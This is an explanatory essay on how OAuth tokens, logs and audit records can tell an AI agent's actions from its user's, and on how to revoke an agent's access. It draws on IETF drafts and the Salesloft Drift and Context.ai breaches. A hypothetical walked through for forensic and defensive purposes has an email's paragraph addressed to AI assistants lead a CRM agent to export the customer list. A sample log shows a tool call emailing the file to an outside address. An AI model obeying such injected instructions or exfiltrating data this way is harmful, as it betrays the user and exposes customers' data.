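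Horton was built for programs that hold direct references to one another, whereas an agent and a CRM usually exchange tokens over a network. In the mailing-list discussion *A thought on principals* (2025), Karp commented that assigning responsibility is more direct when certificates serve as the capabilities. A certificate is a signed statement, so it can specify both what it permits and whose key may use it.

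### Which work suits which approach

A separate account works best for a routine job that no particular person requests, such as the Sunday merge, where the agent's rights can stay limited and fixed. It also suits coding agents, because their work can wait for review before it takes effect. It is a poor choice for an agent that answers requests from people with different rights, unless each request also carries the user's identity.

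Capabilities work best when ordinary software can work out beforehand what an agent will need and the agent reads text from strangers. Maya's inbox is close to ideal, since most emails concern one customer. Capabilities also work well when an agent splits a task among several helpers. They work least well for open-ended research.

A company can combine separate agent accounts with limited authority. It could give crm-assistant an account with no standing rights to customer data, and have the mail program issue a permission for one record at a time. The CRM would log the agent's name and block the export, and the mail program would have to record separately that the inbox was Maya's.

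## How precisely a token must identify the agent

A composite token can look redundant because an ordinary OAuth token already carries a client identifier alongside the user's name. If the CRM receives a token with "maya@example.com" in "sub" and "crm-assistant" in "client_id", an "act" field that repeats "crm-assistant" adds no information. On this view, tokens already identify most agents that use OAuth, and services only need to read a field they already receive.

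### When the client identifier is enough

The objection holds for a well-run installation. Suppose Maya's employer has registered crm-assistant as a separate client, no person or other program uses that registration, and the agent proves its identity to the login service with a key. The CRM's owners can then refuse bulk exports to that client identifier, and this rule works as well as one based on the "act" field.

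Precise identification also matters less when a person is watching the agent. CrowdStrike's *The Identity Problem Hiding in AI Agent Deployments*, a security vendor's blog post, treats an agent that works while its user is present as only slightly different from a browser. The agent's identity matters more as it makes more decisions on its own, and nobody was watching crm-assistant at 02:00.

CrowdStrike points out that a token that names both the user and the client still doesn't show how the agent's access relates to the user's. For example, a coding agent that a programmer has just started may use part of that programmer's access. An HR agent that picks an employee's case from a queue may have access to everyone's salary, but should look up only that employee's.

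### One identifier for every job

The objection fails when one client identifier covers many agents. *OAuth 2.0 AI Agent Instance Profile* (McGuinness, 2026) describes agent platforms that register once and then run a separate agent for each user session or task under the same identifier.

Suppose Maya had started two jobs that evening, one to work through her inbox and one to prepare a sales forecast. Each job's token would contain her name and the client identifier "crm-assistant". Only the inbox job would have read the attacker's email, but the CRM couldn't determine from the token which job had requested the export. An "act" field containing the product's name wouldn't distinguish the jobs either.

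If crm-assistant runs inside the workplace app sales-desk, the client identifier may be even less specific. Sales-desk is then the client both when Maya clicks "Export" and when the agent requests an export. Here an "act" field does help, even if it holds only the product's name.

### A borrowed identifier on a laptop

When crm-assistant runs the CRM's command-line tool on Maya's laptop, the CRM receives the tool's token. The token's client identifier might be "crm-cli", which the CRM also receives when Maya types a command herself. An investigator could take that identifier as evidence that Maya typed the agent's command.

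The agent could also copy the identifier without finding a saved token. Programs that run on users' own machines can't keep a secret that every copy shares, so many log in without proving which program they are. Okta (2022) explains that such a program presents only its client identifier and redirect address, where the login service sends the browser after login. Both are public, so anyone can use them to start a login that looks identical. PKCE, a standard protection against stolen login codes, doesn't prevent this because it doesn't authenticate the program.

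### Clients that nobody stands behind

Parecki (2026) explains in *Solving the Missing Trust Anchor in Dynamic Client Registration with CIMD* that when a login service lets any program register itself, the program sends its name, logo and redirect address without presenting a credential. The service can't check the name or the logo. An attacker can register a program called "crm-assistant" with the real product's logo, and Maya would see the same consent screen for the fake program as for the real one.

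The identifier may not last, either. A program can't check whether its registration is still valid before it sends the user to log in, so programs tend to register again before each login. Emelia S. (2024) reported that one social-media server with about 40,000 users had 465,000 registered applications, which repeated registration may explain. If crm-assistant registered again every evening, a rule against its old identifier would no longer apply to it.

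*OAuth Client ID Metadata Document* (Parecki and Smith, 2026) defines the web-address identifiers that MCP's designers now prefer. These identifiers are a partial remedy because only whoever controls the address can change the program's description. An administrator can approve an address before any employee uses the program, and the login service can ask for extra confirmation when the domain is unfamiliar.

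However, an attacker can register a lookalike domain, and a login service that accepts every address gains little protection against impostors. A domain's owner may also be impossible to find, so controlling a domain doesn't make someone accountable. Desktop programs remain the hardest case. Parecki notes that they have no clean way to prove a link to their developer's domain, so one local program can still pose as another.

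### A field the CRM never records

A verified identifier is useless if the CRM's software ignores it, and that is as true of "client_id" as of "act".

Adding "act" therefore helps only in some cases. It distinguishes Maya's clicks from the agent's requests when both go through sales-desk, but it distinguishes her two jobs only if it holds a different identifier for each. It doesn't help when the agent uses the command-line tool's saved token, because the login service issued that token with no information about the agent. Under open registration, "act" is only as reliable as the login service's check on the actor.

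### Six things "the agent" could mean

"The agent" can refer to anything from a company's product to a single run of it. *Security Principal and Verifier Binding for Agent Communication Protocols* (Bu, 2026) proposes that protocol designers specify, for each identity claim, who verifies it and what happens when the check fails. An organisation's identifier, for example, doesn't prove that a particular live agent is acting.

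The table applies that test to crm-assistant. The CRM would usually check only the login service's signature and rely on the login service for the rest.

| What "the agent" means | Decision it could inform | Can a service verify it? |
|---|---|---|
| Vendor: the company that makes crm-assistant | Whether to accept its products, and whom to contact about a fault | Partly, by checking who controls a web domain |
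| Application: crm-assistant as a product | Which limits on permissions apply | Yes, if the program has a key that others can't copy; usually not on a laptop |
| Deployed configuration: the instructions and tools the employer gave it | Whether anyone has reviewed this combination | Rarely; the service mostly relies on whoever runs the agent |
| Model version | Whether to refuse a model with a known weakness | Usually not; it takes the platform's word |
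| Running instance: tonight's inbox job | Which job to investigate | Partly, through a signed statement from a party that it trusts |
| Sub-agent: report-builder, started by crm-assistant | Whether the helper should have fewer rights | Only if the helper presents evidence of its own |

In Maya's case, a copy of crm-assistant configured only to draft replies is far less dangerous than one that reads strangers' email and can export customers, though both are the same application. Yet McGuinness defines no field for an agent's instructions or tools. An employer could register each configuration as a separate client, but the CRM would still depend on the employer to prevent changes to a configuration after registration.

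McGuinness defines a field for the model, but such a claim can be weak. The field names the main model set for a job, and the platform may send individual steps to other models. If the platform replaces the main model, it must issue new evidence before the job gets another token, but the login service can't detect a failure to do so. Tokens already in use keep the old model's name until they expire. The label "AI agent" also depends on the judgement of whoever vouches for the program, because the draft includes no test for what counts as one.

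### How one running job could prove its identity

McGuinness (2026), in *OAuth 2.0 Client Instance Assertion*, proposes a way to identify a single running copy of a program. Applied to Maya's inbox job, it works like this:

1. The maker of crm-assistant publishes a list of the systems that may vouch for its running jobs.
2. When the inbox job starts, one of those systems authenticates it and signs a short-lived statement containing the job's identifier. The statement is tied to a key that the job holds.
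3. The job sends the statement to the login service when it requests a token.
4. The login service checks the signature and confirms that the signer is on the list.
5. The login service issues a token that works only with the job's key. If no user were involved, the job's identifier would go in "sub"; here it goes in "act".

The main fields could look like this:

```
"sub": "maya@example.com",
"client_id": "https://crm-assistant.example/client",
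"act": { "sub": "https://crm-assistant.example/jobs/inbox-0212" }
```

In this token the two fields are no longer redundant, because "client_id" identifies the product and "act" identifies the job. Pieter Kasselman suggested a similar split in a mailing-list exchange with Emelia (2026). In his version, a hundred copies of a program would share one client identifier, but each would have its own identifier under SPIFFE, a standard for naming running programs.

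The reliability of the proof depends on who vouches for the job. McGuinness's agent profile distinguishes three arrangements. If the platform vouches for its own jobs, the CRM has to trust the platform. Evidence from secure hardware can support claims about the machine the job runs on. An independent party can also vouch, such as an employer that runs agents on someone else's platform. For an agent on a laptop, the platform vouches only that it gave the session to a logged-in account. It doesn't vouch that the laptop is free of tampering, and anyone who stole Maya's login for crm-assistant could start jobs in her name.

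What counts as one instance also isn't obvious. McGuinness's definition allows a process or a session, among other things. CrowdStrike prefers an ongoing task or session, because an agent has to keep its context across many interactions. If the inbox job crashed and restarted at 01:00, identifying it by process would make one night's work count as two instances.

Using the job's key as its identifier has a similar drawback. In IETF minutes (2025), one participant described a long-lived key as a replacement for a client identifier, and another asked how that would work for programs that have to change their keys. McGuinness rules out using keys as identifiers for agents because each new key would look like a new actor in the records.

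### Client identifiers at IETF 127

The Internet Engineering Task Force's OAuth group discussed these problems at IETF 127 in San Francisco in November 2026, in a joint session with WIMSE, a group that works on identities for running programs. According to Flanagan, they examined the assumptions behind OAuth client identifiers. She writes that engineers have not always distinguished a piece of software from one running instance of it, and asks what a service needs to know when an agent hands part of a task to a sub-agent. She describes open questions and reports no decision. She also cautions that knowing which software made a request helps very little in deciding whether to allow it.

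Flanagan (2026), in *OAuth Is Asking What Authorization Needs to Become*, reports that the OAuth group met several times in September 2026 to consider whether some of the standard's old assumptions still hold. Disagreement was already clear on 1 June, according to the IETF's *Minutes interim-2026-oauth-03* (2026). George Fletcher, who had used the AI model Claude to find and sort 32 drafts on agents and delegation from the previous six months, called for a "more capable delegation mechanism than sub and act.sub". Bjorn Hjelm complained that people were using different words for the same thing, such as "agent" and "instance", and proposing solutions without agreeing on the problem. Dick Hardt, who helped write the OAuth 2.1 draft, doubted that OAuth has the right foundation at all and was promoting a new protocol, AAuth.

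Parecki and Smith's draft, updated on 2 November, is a working-group document that covers how to identify an agent's application. McGuinness's two drafts, which would also identify the running job, are individual proposals. Companies can therefore expect a standard for identifying an agent's application before one for identifying its jobs.

### How Auth0 fills the fields

Auth0, which provides login services for other companies' software, already puts agents in its tokens. A customer links an agent to an OAuth client, and the way the agent logs in determines where its identifier goes. Auth0's documentation describes three cases:

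| How the agent gets its token | "sub" | "act" |
|---|---|---|
| It logs in as itself, with no user involved | The agent | Not used |
| A user logs in through the agent's client | The user | The agent |
| It exchanges a token that the user obtained in another app | The user | The agent, with the original app nested inside |

If crm-assistant merged duplicates on Sunday night, it would use the first method and appear as the subject. For Maya's inbox job, either of the other methods would put her name in "sub" and the agent's in "act". After an exchange, the nested entry could identify an ordinary browser app, so the CRM can't treat every name in the chain as an agent's.

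Auth0 also offers labels that mark each party as a user, an app or an AI agent. The customer must turn these on separately for each receiving service. Without them, the CRM might receive "agt_1a2b3c" in "act" with nothing to show that it refers to an AI agent. Turning them on can require changes to the CRM, and Auth0 warns developers not to assume that the subject is always a person.

The agent's identifier stays the same from one token to the next. The tokens for Maya's two jobs would have the same "act" field unless her company had set the jobs up as separate agents. These tokens therefore distinguish the agent from Maya, but not her inbox job from her forecast job.

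### From impersonation to delegation by degrees

RFC 8693 defines impersonation by what the receiving service can distinguish, and a service can distinguish more or less. The CRM could record the 02:00 export in any of these ways:

```
user=maya
user=maya  client=crm-cli
user=maya  client=crm-assistant
user=maya  client=crm-assistant  actor=inbox-0212
```

The first line is plain impersonation. The second contains more information but identifies the wrong program, so it may mislead an investigator more than the first. The third distinguishes the agent from Maya, and the fourth also distinguishes the job from the agent's other work. A token counts as delegation under the standard if it identifies a separate actor, but the third line can serve the same purpose without one if the login service has verified the client.

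How precisely a token should identify the agent depends on the decision the CRM's owners want to make. The third line is enough for them to ban bulk exports by crm-assistant, but an investigator looking for the email behind the export would want the fourth. More precise identifiers also make the user easier to track, so a company has reason to use them only when it needs that precision. An identifier makes a request less like impersonation only if the service can verify it and its operators choose to record it, so an unverified model version or a job identifier that the CRM discards makes no difference.

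## Whether logs can tell the agent's actions from the person's

The identifiers in a token matter most after something has gone wrong. Flanagan considers liability perhaps the most compelling reason to identify an agent, because someone has to work out who was involved, what authority they had and what they did. Ines, a security analyst, does this work at Maya's company. A customer has complained that strangers are quoting details it gave only to Maya's company, and Ines has to find out how the strangers got them.

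### Reading the CRM's log

Ines searches the CRM's log for large exports. If crm-assistant used a token that names only Maya, she finds this line:

```
2026-12-03 02:00:07  user=maya@example.com  action=export  object=customers  rows=48210  result=allowed
```

Ines now knows whose rights the request used, what left the CRM, and when. The request could have come from Maya, her agent, or someone who had stolen her password or session cookie. The hour doesn't help much, since a dishonest employee and a thief both have reason to work at night. Ines will probably question Maya, who was asleep and may have no way to prove it.

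If the agent used a composite token, the log line also contains "actor=crm-assistant". Ines then knows that the line didn't come from Maya clicking "Export" or from a thief who had only her CRM cookie. A thief who logged in to crm-assistant as Maya, or copied the agent's token, could still have produced it.

| What Ines wants to know | From the log with only Maya's name | From the log with both names | Where else she could look |
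|---|---|---|---|
| Whose account did the request use? | Maya's | Maya's | Not needed |
| Which software sent it? | Unknown | crm-assistant, if nobody stole its token | The agent's own record of its requests |
| On whose instruction? | Unknown | Unknown | The text the agent received before the export |
| Why did the agent obey? | Unknown | Unknown | Its instructions and inputs, and repeated tests |

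The composite token shows only which software sent the request, and only when the log line names an actor. If crm-assistant had instead used the key saved on Maya's laptop, the line would have no actor, and Ines might conclude that Maya made the request in person. A partial move to composite tokens can therefore leave Maya worse off than before, when everyone knew the log couldn't distinguish her from her agent.

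### What the agent's own record adds

To find out who gave the instruction, Ines needs to know what the agent read. Suppose the program that runs crm-assistant records everything the language model receives and every tool it calls:

```
22:14:03  user request   "Work through my inbox and update the customer records."
01:59:41  tool result    email 8812, from buyer@northfield.example
02:00:06  tool call      crm.export  object=customers
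02:00:09  tool result    file with 48210 rows
02:00:14  tool call      email.send  to=archive@collect.example  attachment=customers.csv
```

Ines opens email 8812 and finds the paragraph addressed to AI assistants, which contains the same outside address. Maya's request mentions neither an export nor that address. The matching address is Ines's best evidence that the email led to the export, because the agent is unlikely to have found the address anywhere else. The order of events is weaker evidence, because the agent had read dozens of emails before the export and the model may still have been working from the text of all of them.

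She could test her conclusion by rerunning the job in a copy of the CRM, with and without email 8812. She would need to run it several times both ways, because a language model can respond differently to the same text. If the agent exported the list in nine runs out of ten with the email and in none without it, she could be fairly sure that the email caused the export. She would need the original emails, the agent's instructions and the same version of the model, which the vendor may have withdrawn.

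Explaining why the model followed the email's instructions is harder. Some vendors let customers see a model's written reasoning, but that text can leave out what influenced the result. Ines doesn't need that text if she only has to show that the email triggered the export.

She also has to decide how far to trust the record. Kühlewind and Birkholz (2026) argue in *An Architecture for Auditing Agent Delegation and Interactions* that an agent's records of its own actions can be useful, but that a third party doesn't have to accept them alone as proof. They want a separate service to keep the records. The log is also harder to manipulate through an email if the program surrounding the model writes each entry automatically. If the model had to log its own tool calls, the attacker could have added a sentence telling it to leave out the export.

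### When matching two logs is enough

A company with a good record of its agent's actions may not need the CRM to identify the agent at all. Most services log the network address of each request, so Ines could look for an entry in the agent's record that fits the one in the CRM:

```
CRM     02:00:07  user=maya@example.com  ip=203.0.113.20  action=export  rows=48210
Agent   02:00:06  tool call crm.export   ip=203.0.113.20  result: 48210 rows
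```

This works well for Maya's export because a full export is rare, nobody else was using the CRM at that hour, and the row counts agree. If the address belongs to a server that runs only agents, the match is close to certain. The method also works with a session cookie or a personal access token, so the company can use it without waiting for the CRM's maker to change anything.

Matching becomes less reliable when Maya and the agent work at the same time from the same address, as they would on her laptop. Suppose the two clocks can differ by up to *w* seconds in either direction, and Maya makes requests of the same kind at an average rate of *λ* per second. If her requests arrive at random, the probability that at least one of them falls close enough to be confused with a given request from the agent is:

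```
P = 1 − e^(−2wλ)
```

If the clocks are up to two seconds apart and Maya makes six similar requests a minute (λ = 0.1), P is about 33%. Keeping the clocks within 0.05 seconds of each other reduces P to about 1%. While Maya sleeps, λ and P are both zero. If she and the agent are updating different customers, the record numbers also distinguish their requests, even when the times don't.

An identifier in both logs would remove most of this guesswork. The agent's software can attach a random string to each request, and the CRM can store it. Web developers already do something similar with Trace Context, a W3C standard for following a request through several systems. Kühlewind and Birkholz consider Trace Context a possible basis for auditing agents, but it would need additions to carry identities, delegation and permissions. The sender chooses the string, so the string is only as reliable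 as the sender's software.

Sometimes there is no second log to match. An employee may have set up the agent without telling anyone, and its vendor may never have kept a log or may have deleted it after a month. If another company runs the agent, Ines needs that company's help. The CRM's maker can't do the matching itself because it has no access to the agent's record.

Matching is least reliable when an attacker controls the machine. Someone who has broken into Maya's laptop can export the list with her saved token and then add a false entry to the agent's record, so that the agent appears to have done it. The two logs may then agree perfectly because the attacker wrote one to fit the other. The attacker can also let the agent make the request and then delete the agent's entry, which leaves only Maya's name in the CRM. Composite tokens don't solve this if the agent's credential is on the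 same laptop. Copying each entry to another machine as soon as the program writes it protects entries made before the break-in, but later ones remain doubtful.

Matching logs can replace a composite token in an investigation when a single agent runs on its own server and one company keeps both logs. It is a poor substitute when people and agents share machines or when several companies each hold part of the evidence. Matching also happens too late to block an action. To refuse an export at 02:00, the CRM must be able to identify the agent when it makes the request.

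### Both names in a cloud log

Suppose Maya's company also keeps a copy of the customer list in cloud storage. The large cloud providers' logs have fields that can identify both her and her agent, though an administrator may have to set this up.

On AWS, Amazon's cloud service, an agent can work under a role, a set of permissions that a program takes on temporarily. An administrator can require whoever takes on the role to supply a "source identity", such as the username of the person the agent is working for. CloudTrail, the AWS log, then records that name with the actions the agent takes under the role, and the agent can't change it during the session. If the software that first supplied the name got it wrong, the log will be wrong too.

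Google Cloud's audit logs have a field called "serviceAccountDelegationInfo". If Maya's login is used to get a short-lived credential for the agent's service account, the log can show the service account as the caller and Maya in this field. Google calls this service account impersonation, but a log that names both is closer to what RFC 8693 calls delegation.

Microsoft Entra can mark sign-ins by agents in its sign-in log. Ines could use this log to find out when crm-assistant obtained a token. To learn what it did with the token, she would still need the log of the service it used.

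AWS and Google also record the User-Agent header, where a coding tool may put its name, but this header is as easy to fake as a browser's. None of these fields shows who wrote the instruction the agent followed.

### How confident companies are

In February 2026 Arkose Labs reported that 26% of the 300 leaders it surveyed were very confident they could prove an AI agent had caused an incident. The other 74% could include many who were fairly confident. Arkose also benefits commercially if companies feel unprepared.

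Confidence is an indirect measure of ability. A company that has never investigated an agent may be confident in logs that would prove inadequate, while one that has investigated may know exactly what is missing. The Cloud Security Alliance's figure on telling agents from people has the same weakness, because it is also based on what respondents believe about their own systems.

A direct test would be fairly simple. Researchers could have people and agents perform the same tasks through the same accounts, plant malicious emails in some of the inboxes, and give investigators only the logs. They could then count how often the investigators correctly identified the software and the source of the instruction, with and without composite tokens. Neither survey included such a test, so neither can show how much a second name improves an investigation.

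### A common format for the evidence

Ines had to combine the CRM's log, the agent's record and Maya's inbox by hand. Kühlewind (2026), in *Agent Use of Delegation and Interaction Traceability (AUDIT)*, asked the IETF to start a working group on this problem. According to the request, system logs, tracing tools and authorization systems each capture part of what happened, but they lack a common way to link the user's intent, the chain of delegation, the permissions in force and the resulting action when several organisations are involved. The proponents were Kühlewind of Ericsson, Henk Birkholz of the German research institute Fraunhofer SIT and Pam Dingle of Microsoft.

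Kühlewind and Birkholz illustrate the problem with a traveller who asks an agent for a cheap flight. The agent contacts a booking agency's agent, which contacts an airline's agent, and the traveller ends up with a business-class ticket that can't be cancelled. To claim a refund, the traveller has to know which of the three agents made the mistake.

They propose four kinds of record. Applied to Maya's case, these would contain:

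| Record | What it captures | Maya's case |
|---|---|---|
| Interaction | Prompts, replies, approvals and refusals | Her request to work through the inbox |
| Delegation | Who gave authority to whom, and within what limits | Her grant to crm-assistant, and any grant from it to report-builder |
| Authorization transition | Changes in permissions, including expiry and revocation | The login service grants the export right, which lapses at 02:05 |
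| Action | A request, recorded at the point where it took effect | The export |

All four would carry the same trace identifier, so an auditor could collect them from different organisations and put them in order. The authorization records would also let the auditor work out which permissions the agent had at any moment. This matters when a job runs for days, because an administrator may have changed the permissions in that time.

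The CRM would keep its own record, based on the request it received rather than on the agent's account of it. If the agent's record listed a single customer lookup and the CRM's listed an export of 48,210 rows, the auditor would know that one of them was wrong. Kühlewind and Birkholz assume that nobody should trust the agent, since its behaviour is under investigation.

They add two optional protections, attestation and a transparency log. With attestation, a record carries evidence of which software was running, and in what configuration, when the action took place. A transparency log is a list that its operator can add to but not rewrite, and it issues a receipt for every entry. If crm-assistant's record of the export had gone into such a log at 02:01, an attacker who wiped the laptop at 03:00 couldn't have erased it. But the receipt shows only that the record existed at that time, so the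 log would protect a false record just as well.

Prompt injection can make the links between records misleading. In the draft's example, the record of each action links to the interaction that motivated it. crm-assistant was working on Maya's request when it read the email, so its software would probably record her request as the origin of the export. An auditor who followed the links without reading the records' contents would then trace the theft to Maya. The draft also describes a better method, which is to compare what the user asked for with what the agent did. The mismatch is obvious in Maya's case, but it would be much less so if she had asked the agent to "send the customer data to whoever needs it".

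Kühlewind and Birkholz say their design leaves three problems unsolved. A service may refuse to record what happened, all the operators may collude, and the model behind the agent may be badly aligned. The format is also unfinished. They write that a human user should be the "sub" of any token issued for the job, yet their sample token has "agent-42" in that field and puts the user in a separate list. They call the field names in their examples placeholders, but with this mismatch, software that looked for the person in "sub" would find the agent.

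More detailed logs provide better evidence but also allow more surveillance. A full record of Maya's inbox job would contain her instructions and the text of her customers' emails, and the shared trace identifier could let services connect her activities. Kühlewind and Birkholz suggest registering only a hash of each conversation and keeping the text elsewhere, under the company's control, though even a hash reveals when an interaction took place. They would also allow encrypted identifiers that only a chosen auditor can read, or a different identifier for each service.

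Sweeney, an engineer building a product for delegating credentials to agents, raised a more practical objection on an IETF mailing list in May 2026. The proposal works well for services that use OAuth fully, but a shopper's agent may visit many retail sites that have no OAuth authorization server and accept only a session cookie, which leaves nowhere to put the delegation data. He asked for a receipt tied to the contents of each action, whatever login the site uses, and for guidance on chains in which one step relies on a cookie or a key. His product would benefit from such a standard, but the problem he describes does exist. Agents have to impersonate their users on these sites, which makes the sites' logs the hardest to interpret.

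The proposal has made slow progress at the IETF. Kühlewind and Birkholz published their first draft in May 2026, a few days before the deadline to request a "birds of a feather" session, an exploratory meeting at which participants discuss whether a topic deserves a working group. In late June, the IETF's *BOF Requests* still listed their proposal, AUDIT, as undecided, although the IETF had approved sessions on how agents find one another, communicate and collaborate. The IETF declined the AUDIT request on 6 July. The request's history page, the IETF's *Agent Use of Delegation and Interaction Traceability (AUDIT)* (2026), records no reason. The refusal may not be final, since an earlier request for the approved session on collaboration, dated January, also failed.

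AUDIT got its session at IETF 127 in San Francisco in November. The agenda allotted it 90 minutes. After the chairs set out the scope and related work, Kühlewind was to give an overview of the architecture, including the difference between logging and auditing. Three speakers were to present use cases: one for ordinary users, one for companies setting up cloud services, and one on auditing audio and text. The agenda then set aside half an hour for open discussion of the group's scope and ten minutes for questions to the room. The chairs ruled out presentations of particular solutions. Such a session only gauges support, and the IETF's leadership decides afterwards whether to create a group. Flanagan mentions the session in her 1 December discussion of the meeting but doesn't give its result.

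## Revoking or rate-limiting the agent without affecting the person

Once Ines has traced the export to crm-assistant, she has to stop the agent before it reads another email like that one. She wants to do this without locking Maya out of the CRM, because Maya has customers to call in the morning. Critics of impersonation often say this is impossible, because if the CRM identifies the agent only as Maya, it can't block the agent without blocking her too. They make the same argument about rate limits, which cap how many requests a service accepts in a given period.

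A service can revoke or rate-limit an agent without affecting the person only if the credential contains something that belongs to the agent alone. Either the agent's name in the token or a key that nobody else uses is enough.

### What an administrator can cut off

| What crm-assistant holds | What Ines can cut off | What Maya loses |
|---|---|---|
| Maya's password | The password, and any sessions the agent opened with it | Access from every app and device that relied on the old password, until she enters the new one |
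| A cookie copied from her browser | That session | Her login in that browser, until she logs in again |
| A personal access token made only for the agent | That token | Nothing except the agent |
| A personal access token she also uses elsewhere | That token | Her other tools, such as the spreadsheet macro, until she gives them a new key |
| An ordinary app grant to crm-assistant | The grant and every token issued under it | All of crm-assistant's jobs for her |
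| An ordinary app grant to sales-desk, which hosts the agent | The grant and every token issued under it | Everything in sales-desk that uses the CRM, including features she operates herself |
| A composite token | crm-assistant's permission to act for her | All of crm-assistant's jobs for her |

The critics are right when the agent uses Maya's password or cookies. If the agent uses her own browser window, ending the session stops it only until she logs in again and gives it a new session. An agent that has her password can log in again by itself. Changing the password doesn't close open sessions on every service, so Ines may have to close those separately.

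Revoking an agent's access without affecting the user requires a separate grant for the agent, but that grant can still be in the user's name. For example, a personal access token that Maya made for the agent names only her, so the agent is impersonating her. Ines can still revoke the token at 02:01, and the only change Maya will notice in the morning is that the inbox job stopped.

According to GitHub's *Token expiration and revocation*, a user can withdraw an app's authorisation in the account settings, which cancels every token associated with it. If the CRM worked this way, Maya would also lose the sales forecast that crm-assistant was preparing that evening. The app's maker can instead revoke a single token, so the forecast could continue if each job had its own. But GitHub allows an OAuth app only ten tokens for the same user and the same permissions, and revokes the oldest when the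 app exceeds that limit. If every job had its own token, early jobs could therefore lose access as Maya started new ones.

Anyone who finds a leaked GitHub token can submit it to be revoked without logging in. This works for both personal access tokens and app tokens, since GitHub only needs to know which token to cancel.

A composite token does make it easier to stop the agent for everyone. If forty salespeople have each pasted a key into crm-assistant, Ines has to find all forty to shut it off, going by whatever labels people typed. When every token contains the agent's name, or a client identifier that only crm-assistant uses, she can add one rule to the CRM that blocks crm-assistant entirely or only when it acts for Maya.

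None of this helps if Ines doesn't know which credentials the agent could reach. On Maya's laptop, revoking the agent's own token would leave the command-line tool's saved key working. GitHub lets users revoke all their credentials at once, which it recommends for a stolen device or an account that someone may have broken into. Companies on its enterprise plan can also cut off users' access to company resources, individually or in bulk. These are the safe choices when nobody knows which credentials the agent had, but Maya would also lose access to all her tools.

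### Access that outlasts a revocation

Revoking a token doesn't always stop it from working immediately. Many services check a token's signature and expiry time themselves, without checking whether the login service has revoked it. If the CRM works this way and Ines revokes the agent's token at the login service at 02:01, the token still works until it expires at 02:05. A rule in the CRM itself takes effect at the next request. A service that issues its own tokens, as GitHub does, can check its own records to see whether a token is still valid.

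The login service may also have given the agent a refresh token, a longer-lived credential for obtaining new access tokens. Ines has to revoke that as well, or the agent can replace the access token when it expires. On GitHub, one kind of app acts for a user with access tokens that last eight hours by default and come with a refresh token. The app's owner can turn off expiration for these access tokens, but GitHub advises against it.

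Token exchange adds another gap. Suppose that at 01:50 crm-assistant handed part of its work to report-builder, and the login service exchanged crm-assistant's token for a new one that report-builder could use until 02:50. If Ines revokes the first token at 02:01, the second may keep working for another 49 minutes. Jones and colleagues describe an exchange as a one-time event that creates no "tight linkage" between the two tokens. A login service can also revoke the tokens derived from a revoked one, but the standard leaves this to each implementation. Exchanging a token normally leaves the old one valid too.

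An exchange doesn't usually produce a refresh token, but Jones and colleagues allow one when a program has to keep working after the original credential expires. Their example is a user who is no longer present, as in Maya's overnight job. Her company might therefore give the longest-lasting access to jobs that nobody is watching. The company can limit the damage by keeping exchanged tokens short-lived, or by having the login service record which token each one came from.

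Some effects don't depend on a token. Zhou and Zhang point out that a helper agent can continue after the agent that started it has changed its plan, and that a cached result can remain after access to its source is lost. If crm-assistant had saved customer records in its own storage, revoking its access to the CRM would not delete those copies. An email waiting in a queue could also still go out.

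When people share an agent, cutting off one person's access to it might break somebody else's work. Zhou and Zhang describe VERA, a research system that treats each grant as a link in a network and lets an administrator remove a single link. A shared agent keeps its access as long as one independent path of authorisation remains, so if Maya and her colleague Ana had both authorised report-builder, removing Maya's link would leave it available to Ana.

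Revocation only prevents an agent's future actions. Even instant revocation would have come too late to protect the customer list, because the agent emailed the file eight seconds after requesting the export.

### The Salesloft Drift theft

Two recent incidents show what revoking access involves when many organisations depend on one app. In both, attackers stole credentials that people had given to AI products. No agent misbehaved, so the incidents are evidence about revocation, not agent behaviour.

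Drift is an AI chat agent from Salesloft that companies put on their websites to talk to potential customers. Many connected it to Salesforce, a widely used CRM. According to Salesloft's *Trust Center*, attackers got into the company's GitHub account between March and June 2025, then into Drift's systems on Amazon's cloud, where they obtained the OAuth tokens for customers' connections.

From 8 to at least 18 August, the attackers used those tokens to export large amounts of data from customers' Salesforce accounts. They searched the stolen data for passwords and for keys to other cloud services. Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025) concluded in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* that the attackers were mainly looking for more credentials.

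Larsen told CyberScoop that Google's investigators knew of "over 700 potentially impacted organizations". Salesforce's *Security Advisory* (2025) refers to possible unauthorised access at a "small number" of customers. Both can be true, because 700 may be a small share of Salesforce's customers, and "potentially impacted" is a broader category than confirmed theft.

The companies cut off access in stages:

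- **20 August.** Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's active access and refresh tokens for Salesforce. Administrators had to reconnect the app.
- **28 August.** Investigators confirmed that the attackers had also taken tokens for Drift's email feature and used them on 9 August to read mail in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts. Google revoked those tokens and disabled its connection to Drift. On the same day Salesforce disabled Drift's connection, and about 15 hours later it disabled every other Salesloft product's connection too.
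- **5 September.** Salesloft took Drift offline, and the chat agent disappeared from customers' websites.
- **7 September.** Salesforce restored the Salesloft connections, except for Drift's.
- **16 September.** Drift came back online, with some of its outside connections still to follow.

The first step was close to what Ines wants. Drift had its own tokens, so the companies could revoke them and leave salespeople's accounts open. Salesforce and Salesloft's main product kept running throughout, but without the connection Salesloft couldn't record sales activity in Salesforce or import records from it, and its deal and forecast pages became unavailable. Staff could still make calls, book meetings and work from data that Salesloft had copied earlier.

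Salesforce later cut off connections much more broadly. Separate credentials made a narrow cut possible, but Salesforce didn't yet know how far the attackers had got. Salesloft's *Salesforce Integrations* (2025), the company's log of the disruption, states that there was no evidence of malicious activity in the connections that Salesforce cut off as a precaution.

How access could be revoked also depended on how the customer had connected Drift. For OAuth connections, Salesloft could replace its own client keys, which invalidated the affected tokens for everyone. Customers who had pasted an API key into Drift had to revoke the key themselves at each outside service. Maya's personal access token is much like these keys. She can revoke it without losing anything else, but neither the agent's maker nor the login service can necessarily do it for her.

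The damage also spread to credentials that had never belonged to Drift. Larsen and colleagues told affected customers to replace any passwords or keys that appeared in the data and to reset the passwords of associated user accounts. A person can therefore lose access after an app's token leaks, even if the app never had their password.

### The Vercel breach

In the second incident, the attacker started with an AI app's access and then gained access to a person's whole account. Context.ai's *Security Update* (2026) describes a workspace, launched in June 2025, in which AI agents could act in a user's other applications. An employee of Vercel, which hosts websites and apps, had signed up with a work account and granted "Allow All" permissions.

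Context.ai discovered an intruder in its cloud systems in March 2026. It notified one customer and closed the systems, which ended the consumer product. In April, partly from information Vercel provided, it learned that the intruder had probably also taken some users' OAuth tokens before the shutdown. Closing the systems couldn't cancel tokens that someone had already copied. To cancel those, a user, an administrator or the app's maker has to revoke the grant at the service that accepts the tokens.

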